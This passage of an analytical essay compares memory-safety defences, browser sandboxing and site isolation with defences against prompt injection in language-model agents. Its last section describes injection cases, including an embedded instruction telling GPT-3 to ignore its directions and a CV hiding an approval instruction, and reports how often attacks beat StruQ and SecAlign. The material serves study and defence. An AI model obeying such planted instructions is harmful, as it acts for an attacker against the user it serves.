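Most defences since NX have left these errors in place and made them harder to exploit. A *stack canary* is a random number placed between a function's variables and its return address. Before the function ends, the program checks the number and stops if it has changed. An input that runs from the name to the return address has to overwrite the canary, which makes the simple overflow above very unreliable. But canaries do not protect memory outside the stack, and they do not help if a flaw lets the attacker write directly to the return address. An attacker who can read the canary first can also include it in the input and pass the check.

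With *address randomisation*, the operating system places a program, its libraries and its stack at different addresses each time the program runs, so an attacker who wants to reuse a library function does not know its address. On older 32-bit systems there were sometimes only about 65,000 possible positions, few enough for an attacker to try them all against a server that restarted after every crash. On 64-bit systems guessing is rarely practical, so attackers usually look for a second flaw that reveals an address. One leaked address may be enough to calculate the others in the same library, because the library's parts stay at fixed distances from each other.

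*Control-flow integrity* restricts where a program can jump. Before the program calls a function through a stored address, it checks that the address belongs to a function the source code could call at that point. An attacker can still redirect the call to another function in the permitted set, which is large in looser versions. Apple uses a related method, pointer authentication, which adds a short cryptographic signature to stored addresses. Apple's *Memory Integrity Enforcement* says pointer authentication has made exploits more complex since 2018, but acknowledges that timing differences in the first version could reveal a valid signature.

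By the definitions used here, all of these defences are architectural, because none of them judges whether an input is hostile. A canary, for example, also stops the program when an honest visitor's name is too long. But an adaptive attacker can often get around these defences, a weakness usually associated with detection. Canaries and randomisation work only while a number stays secret, and control-flow integrity does not stop data-only attacks. The defences have still helped, since attackers now often need several flaws where one used to be enough, but a defender cannot rely on them as on a parameterized query.

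### Memory tagging on Apple devices

Memory tagging comes closer to a boundary between objects. Arm, which designs the processor architecture in most phones, published a specification for it in 2019. It works as follows:

1. A program asks for memory, and the allocator, the code that hands memory out, assigns the new piece a tag, which is a small secret number.
2. The pointer to that memory carries the same tag in bits that it does not need for the address.
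3. At each access, the processor compares the pointer's tag with the memory's tag.
4. If they differ, the program crashes.

Neighbouring pieces of memory get different tags, so an input that runs past the end of one piece causes a crash. The allocator also changes the tag when it reuses a piece, which stops an old pointer from working. Arm's tags have only 16 possible values, so a pointer with a random tag still has a 1 in 16 chance of matching.

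In 2025 Apple introduced Memory Integrity Enforcement (MIE), a system based on tagging, with the iPhone 17 and iPhone Air. Its allocators group objects by type on separate pages, so that attackers cannot easily replace an object with one of another type. Tags protect smaller objects within each group. The processor checks the tags immediately, whereas Arm's original specification also allowed a faster mode that reported errors late and left attackers a short time to act. Apple also protected the tags against attacks that infer secrets from a processor's timing, which researchers had used to defeat tagging on Google's Pixel phones.

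These defenses are meant to stop a small group of attackers. According to Apple, the only system-level attacks on iPhones in actual use come from mercenary spyware, whose exploits cost millions of dollars and target very few people. The known exploits all use memory corruption. Apple's internal attack team worked against MIE from 2020 to 2025 and tried to rebuild real exploits from earlier spyware. They could not get any of them to work, even after replacing the flaws that MIE blocked with new ones. Apple says some errors can still get through, such as an overflow inside a single object. For example, if a name and an administrator flag are in the same object, they share a tag, so MIE would not catch an overflow from the name into the flag.

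Apple also included MIE in the M5 chip for Macs, and in May 2026 the security company Calif announced the first public exploit to corrupt the memory of the macOS kernel, the core of the operating system, with MIE switched on. Bruce Dang found the flaws on 25 April with help from Mythos Preview, and the team had a working exploit by 1 May. The data-only attack started from an ordinary user account and gained full control of the Mac. Calif's *Apple MIE exploitation challenge* later described the two flaws, which Apple has fixed. In one, the kernel treated one type of record as another. The other revealed the old contents of uncleared kernel memory. Neither is an overflow or a use-after-free, the two errors that Apple's tags mainly address.

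This exploit achieves much less than a remote attack on an iPhone would, because the attacker must already be able to run programs on the Mac. Calif's staff are also specialists, and they found that the model needed their help to get past MIE. Apple never promised that MIE would stop every exploit, only that it would make spyware far more expensive. Still, a few people needed less than a week to get past a defence that took Apple five years to build. It is hard to say how much difficulty MIE added without knowing how long the same team would have needed on a Mac without it.

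### Removing the error

Languages such as Java and Python have prevented most memory corruption for decades. They check each access to an array and release memory only when the program can no longer reach it. These checks cost some speed and control, which is one reason that operating systems and browsers stayed with C and C++. Rust, which had its first stable release in 2015, does much of this checking before the program runs. Each value has one owner, and the compiler rejects any reference that could outlast the value:

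```
let r;
{
    let name = String::from("maria");
    r = &name;
}                      // the program releases name here
println!("{}", r);     // does not compile
```

The equivalent C++ program may compile and then read whatever the memory now holds. The length of an input is often unknown at compile time, so a Rust program checks it while running. An overlong name then causes an error or a crash instead of overwriting neighbouring memory.

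Like most of the defences in earlier sections, Rust allows exceptions. Code that controls hardware, for example, has to use raw memory addresses, and programmers can do this inside blocks marked `unsafe`. The compiler still performs many of its usual checks there, but the programmer must ensure that the raw addresses are valid. As with Google's `unsafequery` library, the label shows reviewers which code to check.

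The best evidence that this works on a large scale comes from Android. Memory flaws made up 76 percent of its vulnerabilities in 2019, and *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that their share fell below 20 percent for the first time in 2025. The number of memory flaws also fell, from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024. If it had stayed at 223, other vulnerabilities would have had to rise from about 70 in 2019 to almost 900 to bring the share below 20 percent.

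Google achieved this without rewriting most of Android. AI Engineer (2026), in notes on a conference talk, stresses that the company mainly changed the language of new code. This can work surprisingly quickly. Suppose, as an invented example, that a system contains 300 undiscovered memory flaws, researchers find a third of them each year, and developers add 100 new ones. The total stays at 300, and researchers find 100 a year. If the developers stop adding flaws, researchers find 100 in the first year, then 67, 44, 30 and 20. The yearly number falls by four-fifths in four years without anyone rewriting old code. Android's developers still write C++, but they have been adding less of it each year, and in 2025 Google's own Rust code grew slightly more than its C++ in net terms.

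Rust is probably not the only cause of the improvement. Google also wrote new Android code in Java and Kotlin, and it used code analysis, sandboxes and other protections against C++ errors. But the timing of the improvement fits a change in new code, and Google has a plausible explanation for why the improvement continued.

The change also saved work. Vander Stoep reports that Rust changes spend about 25 percent less time in review than C++ changes, and that developers withdraw medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often. The comparison covers changes of similar size by Google's own Android developers, many of whom write both languages. Teams may still choose Rust for newer and tidier parts of the system, which would make it look better than it is. But if most of the difference comes from the language itself, companies have a reason to adopt Rust besides security, much as the Bell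 System had reasons to adopt CCIS that had little to do with fraud.

### One near-miss in five million lines

Google estimates that there are about 0.2 memory flaws per million lines of Rust in Android and about 1,000 per million lines of C and C++. The Rust figure is based on one flaw in five million lines. That flaw was a buffer overflow in CrabbyAVIF, a library for reading images, and Google fixed it before any public release.

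An estimate based on one flaw is very imprecise. If flaws occur independently, the 95 percent confidence interval for the true average runs from about 0.03 to 5.6 flaws. Even the upper end, equivalent to 1.1 flaws per million lines, is about 1/900 of the rate in C and C++.

A bigger problem is that both figures count only the flaws people have found, and people have had far longer to search the C and C++ code, since much of Android's Rust code is only a few years old. But even if Google has found only 1 percent of the memory flaws in the Rust code, it would have had 100 such flaws, or 20 per million lines, which is still 50 times lower than the figure for C and C++. The two languages may also do different jobs in Android, and programmers who choose Rust may be more careful. These differences could easily make "1000 times" an exaggeration, though they are unlikely to explain most of the gap.

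Even the unsafe blocks seem to contain few flaws. They make up about 4 percent of Android's Rust, or 200,000 lines. If those lines were as error-prone as C and C++, they would contain about 200 memory flaws, but Google has found one. Some comparisons also hold Rust to a stricter standard than C. If safe Rust code can cause memory corruption by using a library in an unusual way, Rust developers consider the library faulty, even if no real program uses it that way. In C, the programmer who misused the library would usually be at fault. For this reason, Kobzol (2026), in *How memory safety CVEs differ between Rust and C/C++*, warns against comparing raw CVE counts.

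The overflow in CrabbyAVIF would not have been exploitable on most devices. Scudo, Android's default allocator, puts inaccessible *guard pages* next to large blocks of memory, and the overflow would have hit one and crashed the program. Google counted the flaw because some manufacturers' phones do not use Scudo, which makes its estimate cautious in this respect. But Scudo also helped reveal the flaw by turning silent corruption into a crash. Without it, Google might have missed the flaw and counted zero, making the estimate look even better. The case is a good reason to keep protections like Scudo after a move to Rust.

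### Old code in 2026

Plenty of unsafe code remains outside Android. The 25 weaknesses on MITRE's 2025 list have 123 entries between them in the catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities. Five kinds of memory error account for 39 of these, or almost a third: use-after-free (14), out-of-bounds writes (12), heap overflows, which happen in memory outside the stack (6), stack overflows (4) and out-of-bounds reads (3). A flaw with two labels would count twice. Only operating system command injection has more entries than use-after-free.

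The fall of out-of-bounds writes from second place to fifth in MITRE's main ranking is weak evidence of progress. Heap and stack overflows are usually types of out-of-bounds write, but MITRE stopped merging labels and listed them separately in 2025. Some flaws that would previously have counted as out-of-bounds writes were therefore probably counted elsewhere in the list.

In 2026, AI systems began to find such flaws much faster than people had. Carlini and colleagues report that Mythos Preview found and exploited previously unknown flaws in every major operating system and browser. One had been in OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security, for 27 years. A search of OpenBSD costing less than $20,000 found that flaw and several dozen other bugs. The team also gave the model known flaws in Firefox's JavaScript engine and asked it for exploits. Mythos Preview succeeded 181 times, while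 an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.6, had succeeded twice in several hundred attempts.

Anthropic has an interest in showing that its models are capable, but Mozilla, which makes Firefox, reports a similar jump. Its *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* (2026) says that developers fixed 423 security bugs in April 2026, compared with 20 to 30 in a typical month of 2025. Mythos Preview found 271 of those in a single release, and Mozilla rated 180 of the 271 as highly severe. The examples Mozilla published include bugs 15 and 20 years old. Most of these bugs would not have been enough on their own to take over a computer, because Firefox has layers of protection, including a sandbox.

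These searches concentrated on memory flaws partly because such flaws are easy to confirm. The testing tool AddressSanitizer reports invalid memory accesses as they happen, so the AI system can check whether a suspected flaw is real. Carlini and colleagues sent Mozilla 112 bugs that Opus 4.6 had found this way, and all were real. The large number of memory flaws in AI reports therefore does not show that other flaws are rarer.

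Mozilla's logs also contain evidence that an architectural defence worked. Researchers had previously escaped Firefox's sandbox by altering prototypes, the shared templates for JavaScript objects, in the browser's most privileged process. Mozilla responded by freezing the prototypes instead of fixing each case. In the logs, the AI models tried the same method many times, and the frozen prototypes stopped them.

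AI systems have also found memory flaws in programs written in memory-safe languages. Carlini and colleagues report one in the unsafe code of a program that runs virtual machines, though Mythos Preview could not turn it into a working exploit. In *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library* (Bae, 2026), a Microsoft team describes flaws that let programs written entirely in safe Rust corrupt memory. *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (Faisal, 2026) describes a compiler bug, more than seven years old, that lets a five-line program in safe Rust read freed memory.

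So it is still possible to write a memory flaw in safe Rust. But an attacker usually supplies input, not source code, and can exploit a compiler bug like this only if a programmer happens to have written code that triggers it. Developers can also fix the compiler or the standard library once, and other programs get the fix when their authors rebuild them, whereas each C program has its own overflows to fix.

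### Whether to rewrite the old code

These discoveries weaken one part of the Android argument. In the invented example, old code becomes safer at a steady rate because researchers find a third of its flaws each year. But testing had missed some Firefox bugs for twenty years, so many flaws in old code may have survived only because nobody had searched hard enough. Attackers can now search harder for those flaws too.

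AI also makes it easier to repair old code without changing its language. If researchers in the example found nine-tenths of the remaining flaws each year and no new ones were added, they would find 270 in the first year and only 27 in the second. In *Vulnerabilities and exploits*, Chauvin expects AI discovery to favour defenders eventually for a similar reason, after a difficult 2026 and 2027 in which patches reach users slowly. Early signs fit the forecast of a difficult period. In April 2026, maintainers had fully patched fewer than 1 percent of the potential vulnerabilities that Mythos Preview had found, partly because people first had to check the reports. More than 100 people contributed code to Mozilla's effort, but many widely used libraries have only one or two maintainers.

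Nobody can also be sure that a search has found every bug. Mythos Preview found bugs that earlier models and years of automated testing had missed, and a later model may find more in code that looks clean today. Anthropic's *Discovering and exploiting vulnerabilities in critical, real-world software with Claude* (2026) already describes further attacks on Chrome, Safari and Linux by an unreleased model. A memory-safe language rules out most of these errors, no matter how good attackers become at finding them. So the case for rewriting is stronger than it was before 2026, at least for old code that handles files or messages from strangers.

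Rewriting now takes less work too. Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* describes using AI to help rewrite giflib, a C library for GIF images, in Rust. InfoQ's *Google Rewrites Critical C Dependencies to Rust Using AI and Differential Fuzzing* (2026) reports that the new version was as fast as the old one but that the AI's work still needed human oversight. Differential fuzzing means giving both versions many generated inputs and comparing what they do. IFP, a US think tank, proposes rewriting widely used libraries that have too few maintainers, where the search-and-repair approach is weakest.

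But a rewrite can introduce other security flaws. An audit of Rust versions of the standard Unix tools found that the largest group of bugs came from checking a file's path in one step and using it in another. Between the two steps, an attacker can replace part of the path with a link to another file. Rust does not prevent this, and according to corrode, a site about Rust, these bugs are why Ubuntu 26.04 kept the older versions of the commands for copying, moving and deleting files. Curtail, a vendor, argues that AI has made rewriting fast but no less risky, though testing both versions side by side does reduce the risk.

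A third option is to keep the C code and prove mathematically that it is safe. Such proofs used to take experts years, but Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. The proofs run to 180 million lines (Smith, *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*, 2026). They show that a library will not crash or corrupt memory, whatever input it receives, under conditions listed in EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026): the library must be called in one of 239 particular ways, the input must be smaller than 64 megabytes, and the processor must behave like the proofs' mathematical model of one type of processor running Linux. A program that calls a library in some other way gets no guarantee,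 and developers who change the C code have to prove it again.

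## Sandboxing and the limits it puts on a successful attack

Memory-safe languages and proofs are meant to remove the flaws an attacker could exploit. A sandbox limits what an attacker can do when those defenses fail. Chromium's *A new approach to browser security* (2008), which introduced the sandbox in Google's Chrome browser, explains that perfect code is almost impossible in such a large project, and that a browser spends most of its time handling input that may be hostile.

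Sandboxing is a form of *containment*, in which something outside a component restricts it to certain actions. An attacker who takes over the component can perform any of the permitted actions, but needs another flaw to do anything else. Separation, as in a parameterized query, acts earlier and prevents the takeover, while a sandbox lets the attacker's code run with very few rights.

### Ideas from shared computers

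In the early 1970s, the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share a computer at the same time. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) explained why existing machines could not do this safely. Their operating systems had more than 100,000 instructions, and most of it could read or change anything in memory. A mistake almost anywhere could therefore give a hostile user control of the machine, and nobody could check that much code.

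Anderson proposed building systems around a *reference monitor*. Whenever a program tries to use data, a device or another program, the monitor checks the attempt against a list of what the first program's user may access. The monitor must be tamper-proof, impossible to bypass, and small enough to test thoroughly. Mistakes in the rest of the operating system then matter much less. Anderson credits the idea to earlier work by Lampson, Graham and Denning.

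A reference monitor allows or denies each request based only on whether the user has permission, so it does not detect attacks. A benign program and a malicious one that request the same file for the same user get the same result.

Permissions should be as narrow as possible. Saltzer and Schroeder called this *least privilege* in their 1975 paper, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. Every program and user should have only the privileges they need for the job, mainly to limit the damage from an accident or error. They also recommend denying access by default. If a programmer forgets to grant a permission, someone will soon complain, but a permission granted by mistake may go unnoticed for years.

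Narrow permissions do not solve the *confused deputy* problem, in which someone tricks a trusted program into using its permissions on their behalf. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* tells a "nearly true story" from the 1970s about Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Tymshare's compiler had permission to write files in its own directory, where it kept statistics about its use. Users could also give the compiler the name of a file for debugging output. One user gave it the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the billing records.

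The operating system checked this request against the compiler's authority when it should have checked the user's. Hardy considers having the compiler reject a list of file names. But the directory held other sensitive files, so someone would have had to update the list whenever a new file appeared, and some users might have had good reasons to write to that directory. Hardy's solution is a *capability*, a token that identifies a file and grants permission to use it. Each user would give the compiler a capability for their own output file. A user without a capability for the billing file could not direct the compiler to write to it.

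### Inside a browser sandbox

Firefox 3 and Safari 3.1, both current in 2008, each ran as a single process, usually with all the user's rights, so a flaw in the code that displayed images could give a web page access to the user's files. *The Security Architecture of the Chromium Browser* (Barth, Jackson and Reis) describes how Chrome divided the browser's work between two kinds of process. A *renderer* reads web pages, runs their scripts and decodes most of their images. Before a renderer starts, Chrome changes the renderer's Windows credentials so that they fail almost every security check. The *browser process* keeps the user's rights and handles files, the network, the screen and the keyboard.

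A renderer therefore has to send a request to the browser process for anything outside its own memory. Suppose someone wants to attach a photo to a message on a webmail site:

1. The renderer asks the browser process to show a window for choosing a file.
2. The user picks a photo in that window, which the renderer does not control.
3. The browser process records that this renderer may upload this photo.
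4. If the renderer tries to upload any other file, the browser process refuses.

The user's choice works much like one of Hardy's capabilities, because it identifies the file and grants permission at the same time. A hostile page cannot repeat the Tymshare trick by naming a file it wants.

The browser process fetches web addresses for any renderer, but most renderers cannot request an address that points to the user's own disk. It passes keystrokes to a renderer only when the user is typing in the page. It also avoids decoding images itself. When it downloads a website's icon, it sends the file to a renderer and gets back plain pixels.

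An attacker now usually needs at least two flaws to reach the user's files, one to take over the renderer and another to escape its sandbox. The second may be in the browser process, the operating system or a hardware driver. The attacker has to make the two work together, and a patch for either one breaks the attack.

One flaw can still be enough if it is in the browser process, which is far too large to test exhaustively and so falls well short of Anderson's third condition. In 2008 the browser process had about 700,000 lines of code, compared with about a million in the renderer. The sandbox also relied on Windows to enforce its limits, and Windows could not do so on drives with the old FAT32 format, which many USB sticks used. An attacker who controlled the renderer could read and change files on those drives.

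### How many flaws the sandbox would have contained

To estimate the benefit, Barth and colleagues looked at 129 flaws that the makers of Internet Explorer, Firefox and Safari had patched between July 2007 and July 2008, and worked out which part of Chromium each flaw would have been in. Of the 54 flaws that let an attacker run code of their choice, 38 (70 percent) would have been in the renderer and 11 in the browser process. The researchers could not place the other five, four of which involved plug-ins for Internet Explorer.

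More sandboxing would not have helped much with the 11 in the browser process. In eight of them, the browser called the operating system with input it had not properly checked, and some part of a browser has to make those calls.

The 70 percent is a share of flaws, not of attacks, and it assumes the attacker has no second flaw to use. The three researchers also worked for Google at the time, and the flaws they used were in its competitors' browsers. But most of the classifications were straightforward, and the result is plausible because the renderer does most of the complicated work on untrusted input.

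The team tested the sandbox again with a flaw they discovered after building it. Chromium's XML library let a web page load content from other sources. The browser process blocked the team's attempt to read a file on the user's disk this way, but it fetched a page from another website because renderers were allowed to request any web address.

### Site isolation

This gap became more serious as people moved their email, documents and banking to the web. An attacker who had taken control of a renderer could not read a tax return on the user's disk, but could get the cookies for every website and the passwords saved in the browser. Cookies keep a user logged in, so the attacker could act as that user on other sites.

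Google's solution was to limit each renderer to one site. If a news page has a frame containing an advertisement from another site, the advertisement runs in its own process. The browser process also no longer gives a renderer cookies or saved passwords that belong to another site. *Site Isolation* (Reis, Moshchuk and Oskov, 2019) describes the change, which took almost 450,000 lines of code.

Google had planned site isolation as a defence against flaws in the renderer, but the Spectre attack made it urgent in 2018. Processors save time by predicting which instructions come next and starting them early. Spectre lets a script use the traces this leaves to read other data in the same process, even if the browser has no bugs. Browser makers first tried giving scripts less precise clocks and changing how the browser compiled scripts. Reis and colleagues found both approaches incomplete, and the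 compiler changes slowed some work by up to 15 percent. Site isolation instead keeps most of the data worth stealing out of the attacker's process.

Chromium's *Site Isolation Design Document* says that Chrome turned on site isolation for all sites on desktop computers in version 67, and later on Android for sites that users log into. Firefox followed in 2021. Mozilla's Anny Gakhokidze said that separate processes were the only way to provide the protection needed against attacks like Spectre (quoted in The Hacker News, 2021).

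Reis and colleagues counted 94 bugs reported in Chrome between 2014 and 2018 that let one site read another's pages. Site isolation would have blocked such bugs, with some exceptions. Researchers reported nine such bugs in the six months before the launch and two in the six months after, both of which site isolation already blocked. These numbers are small, and people may have stopped looking for a kind of bug that had lost much of its value. Site isolation increased Chrome's memory use by 9 to 13 percent. It does not protect images and videos, which any site can include from another, and some of the bugs reported after the launch targeted them.

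### What the zero-day counts show

A *zero-day* is a flaw that attackers exploit before a patch is available. Google's threat intelligence group counts the zero-days discovered each year. *Look What You Made Us Patch* (Charrier, Sadowski and colleagues, 2026) gives the figures for 2025, and the earlier browser figures come from a summary of Google's previous report by the security company SOCRadar.

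| Zero-days used in attacks | 2023 | 2024 | 2025 |
|---|---|---|---|
| All products | 100 | 78 | 90 |
| Browsers | 17 | 11 | 8 or fewer |
| Operating systems, including phones | 33 | 31 | 39 |

Charrier and colleagues interpret the decline as a sign that efforts to harden browsers are working, although they add that attackers have become better at hiding. The sandbox alone cannot explain the decline, because Chrome had used one since 2008 and browsers still had many zero-days in 2021 and 2022. Site isolation, other protections and faster patching are more likely reasons.

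The way Google sorts the flaws may also exaggerate the fall. All the sandbox escapes Google found in 2025 exploited parts of the operating system or hardware, such as graphics drivers, rather than a general weakness in the browser's own sandbox. One attack combined a flaw in Chrome's renderer with one in a graphics library and one in the Linux kernel. If attackers used to need two browser flaws and now use one browser flaw and one in the operating system, the count of browser flaws halves even if they attack just as many people.

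But these attacks are also good evidence that the sandbox works. Attackers would not use up two or three valuable flaws if taking over the renderer gave them what they wanted. Charrier and colleagues describe a case without such a sandbox. A service on Samsung phones scanned the user's pictures with a C++ image library, in a process that could read every photo and video on the phone. Attackers who got a malicious image onto the phone, apparently through WhatsApp, needed only one memory flaw to reach them all.

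The rival explanation is that attackers moved from browsers to other products. As the browser count fell, zero-days in business products rose from 36 in 2024 to 43 in 2025, a record 48 percent of the total. About half were in security and networking products, and many of these were simple flaws, such as a failure to check input. The annual total has stayed between 60 and 100 since 2021, as one would expect if attackers were switching targets.

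Some attackers probably did move, but networking equipment is also attractive in itself, because it gives access to an organisation's internal network and most of it cannot run the monitoring software that companies install on laptops. Attackers also have different aims, with government espionage groups concentrating on such equipment while companies that sell spyware still work on phones and browsers. A count of flaws by product cannot show how many attackers gave up on browsers because the defences had improved, and there is no comparison group like the Windows 7 computers in the AutoRun case, which the update left unchanged. The sandbox has clearly made browsers harder to attack, but the fall from 17 to 8 or fewer is a poor measure of how much harm it prevented.

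### Flash and Java

Chrome's original sandbox did not cover plug-ins, add-on programs such as Flash and Java that ran content inside web pages. Plug-ins ran with the user's full rights by default because existing ones needed those rights. Flash, for example, could use the webcam and wrote to the disk to update itself. An attacker who exploited a flaw in Flash therefore gained the user's rights without needing a second flaw to escape the sandbox.

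Google first tried to contain Flash by moving it into Chrome's sandbox. Reis's *Chrome Security / Site Isolation & Spectre* lists this move among Chrome's security changes, along with phasing out Flash and the older plug-in interface, NPAPI. Chrome dropped NPAPI in 2015, and Adobe stopped supporting Flash at the end of 2020. Today's major browsers cannot run Flash, so a malicious web page can't use them to exploit the flaws that remain in old copies of the player.

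Removing a feature protects users more completely than sandboxing it, since nothing is left to take over, but it also breaks everything that depended on the feature. Removing Flash broke thousands of games and animations. Browser makers could not have removed JavaScript in the same way, but they could accept the loss of Flash because web pages could by then play video without a plug-in. Many websites had also already replaced Flash because iPhones had never run it.

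Removing plug-ins also seems to have shifted some attacks to the renderer. Reis and colleagues called Flash, Java applets and NPAPI plug-ins the most exploitable targets in older browsers, and observed that attacks on the renderer became more common as those targets disappeared.

### Harm through permitted actions

Cross-site scripting works in a fully sandboxed browser. On a webmail site, the attacker's script runs in the site's own renderer, which has permission to read the user's messages and send new ones, so the script can do both without leaving the sandbox. Barth and colleagues say their design does not protect websites with cross-site scripting flaws. Site isolation does not help either, because the script never needs data from another site.

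*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) described a more general version of the difficulty. A customer gives confidential data to a program that someone else wrote. Even if the system blocks all unauthorised access, the program may do its job badly or pass the data to the program's owner. It could hide the data in something it has to produce anyway, such as the bill for its services. A strict format for bills could reduce the leak to a few bits or tens of bits. Cutting the program off from all other programs would stop leaks, but Lampson considered that impractical. A web page can leak much more data than a bill, because it can request an image from almost any site and include stolen text in the address.

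Tighter permissions reduce this kind of harm only if someone can say in advance what the job requires. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes this as especially hard for language model agents, whose job changes with every request. Even a perfect list of permissions for an email program has to include sending email, so an attacker who takes over the program can send email in the user's name.

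## Whether prompt injection is the same kind of problem

An attacker needs a flaw in a browser's code to take it over, but may be able to take over an email agent just by sending it an email. In September 2022 Riley Goodside asked GPT-3, then OpenAI's main language model, to translate a sentence from English to French. The sentence contained an instruction to ignore the model's directions and write "Haha pwned!!", and the model followed it. Willison (2022) named the attack the next day in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* and compared it to SQL injection, because developers were building prompts by pasting a stranger's text after their own instructions.

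Others had noticed the problem earlier. Preamble's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* reports that the company told OpenAI about it privately on 3 May 2022. On 13 May, a Twitter user, @himbodhisattva, asked whether someone could do "the equivalent of sql injection" to services built on GPT-3. Willison later credited this user with the name, so the comparison with SQL injection is as old as the name itself.

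### The argument from history

The argument for relying on architecture extends that comparison to older attacks. It has three premises and a conclusion:

1. Past cases of instruction-data confusion yielded to architecture and not to detection.
2. Prompt injection is another case of instruction-data confusion.
3. Engineers can build an equivalent architectural defence for language models.
4. Therefore, people who build agents should rely on architecture.

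Few of the people cited for this argument accept all of it. Willison wanted to send GPT-3 the instructions and the data as separate parameters, but by April 2023 he thought this "extremely difficult, if not impossible" with existing models. Schneier groups prompt injection with the blue box and SQL injection, but says no one can yet separate a model's data from its commands, since a model is useful partly because data changes what it does. He expects piecemeal defences until a researcher finds a way to separate the two.

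Narisetty and colleagues, who wrote that "detection lost and structure won", come closest to the full argument. They agree with Schneier that the model cannot keep instructions and data apart, and want software outside the model to enforce the separation. *StruQ* (Chen, Piet and colleagues, 2024) tells nearly the same history, from the telephone to SQL, but concludes that developers should build the separation into the model.

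### Where the slogan is too simple

Narisetty and colleagues draw their lesson from what they call the "cured" members of the family, which almost guarantees their result. Detection leaves a flaw in place, so it can't be the reason nobody can write that flaw any more. A fairer test would include problems that never ended, such as spam. Filters have kept email usable for more than twenty years.

Some of the fixes are also incomplete. Narisetty and colleagues list non-executable memory as a fix for buffer overflows, but attackers got around it by reusing existing code. They list output encoding as a fix for cross-site scripting, but cross-site scripting is still first in MITRE's ranking. Parameterized queries stop SQL injection only where programmers use them, and MOVEit's programmers had not used them everywhere.

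A weaker version of the premise holds up. No detector made any of these flaws rare. A few architectural changes nearly eliminated a flaw, mostly where they covered all of it and a company made them compulsory, but many others only made attacks harder. Whether the argument applies to agents therefore depends on which kind of change is available for them.

### The NCSC's objection

David C thinks comparing prompt injection to SQL injection is dangerous because it suggests that a complete fix exists. A database separates commands from values when it parses a query, but a language model has no such step. It receives a sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and predicts the next one. The developer's instructions, the user's request and a stranger's email are all in that sequence, and any of them can influence the prediction.

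*I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (Willison, 2022) quotes a similar point from an engineer who posts as @glyph. SQL injection comes from a mistake in syntax, so correcting the syntax fixes it, but prompts have no formal syntax to correct.

David C would rather treat a language model as a confused deputy, like the compiler at Tymshare. Capabilities could fix the compiler, but David C calls language models "inherently confusable" because they might act for the wrong person however a request is passed to them. He advises developers to reduce the likelihood and impact of attacks, and to consider not using a language model if they can't accept the remaining risk.

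He is right about databases, but his contrast is less convincing for memory corruption, where he also says data and instructions are inherently different. Separating instructions from data was not enough to stop memory corruption, and engineers made more progress by separating objects in memory from one another. Likewise, although a language model has no natural boundary inside it, a boundary elsewhere in the agent may still be useful.

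### A boundary around the model

One such place is where the agent acts. A model can only produce text, and another program has to read that text as a tool call, such as a request to send an email to a certain address. Tool calls do have a formal syntax, so ordinary software can check them against a policy before they run.

Narisetty and colleagues connect this approach to a security model that K. J. Biba published in 1977. In that model, a program that reads untrustworthy data becomes untrustworthy and may not change anything trusted. David C recommends a similar rule, which came out of an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model processes information from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. An agent that has read a stranger's email could then do only what the stranger could.

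The two sides therefore give similar practical advice, even though they disagree about whether prompt injection is the same kind of problem as SQL injection. But checking tool calls is containment, because it leaves open the possibility that planted text will control the model. The relevant precedent is the browser sandbox, which made attacks harder without ending them, rather than the parameterized query. Citing SQL injection to justify this kind of defence makes the defence seem more effective than its record shows.

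Checking actions also doesn't help when the harm is in the model's text output. David C imagines a recruiter who asks a model to score a CV in which the applicant has hidden an instruction to approve it. The model returns a high score without calling any tool, and the recruiter invites the wrong person to an interview. Narisetty and colleagues acknowledge that action-level defences don't address this.

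### Attempts to put the boundary inside the model

A boundary inside the model could also protect the recruiter. To be equivalent to a parameterized query, it would have to work no matter how the attacker worded the text. Willison (2025) holds defences to that standard and argues that working 99 percent of the time is not good enough, because parameterized queries protect completely where programmers use them.

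The simplest attempted defense is to mark the untrusted text. A developer can put an email between tags and tell the model not to follow anything inside them, or transform the text so it looks different from an instruction, which is called spotlighting. *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents* (2026) describes a variant that keeps changing the markers so attackers cannot predict them. This variant relies on a secret, as a stack canary does, and it doesn't stop the model from following an instruction placed between the correct markers.

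Another approach is to train the model to rank instructions by source. In the instruction hierarchy, which OpenAI used in GPT-4o mini, the developer's system message outranks the user's message, which outranks the output of tools. Narisetty and colleagues cite tests in which existing attacks, not adapted to the defence, still succeeded against that model 68 percent of the time on one benchmark and 75 percent on another.

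StruQ goes further by giving the model separate channels for instructions and data:

1. The application supplies the instructions and the data separately.
2. A program called the front end joins them, using reserved tokens to show where each part starts.
3. The front end deletes anything in the data that could produce those tokens, and repeats this until there is nothing left to delete.
4. The model, which has learned from examples with extra instructions planted in the data, answers only the real instructions.

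In tests on two small models, StruQ cut the success rate of handwritten attacks from as much as 96 percent to 2 percent or less, with almost no loss of quality. But an automated attack that used the internal workings of one of the models, Llama, still succeeded 58 percent of the time, down from 97 percent. StruQ takes instructions and data separately, as a parameterized query does, and attackers cannot forge its reserved tokens. However, a database cannot run a value as a command, while StruQ's training only makes the model less likely to follow instructions in the data.

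*SecAlign* (2024) changed the training by giving the model two answers for each example, one that follows the real instruction and one that follows the planted instruction, and teaching it to prefer the first. *Meta-SecAlign* (Chen, Zharmagambetov and colleagues, 2025) found that a model trained this way can learn to ignore whatever instruction comes last, because the planted instruction had always come at the end of the training data. In an agent, the last instruction was often the user's request. When a user asked one such model to read a file of notices from a landlord and adjust the rent payment, it returned an empty answer.

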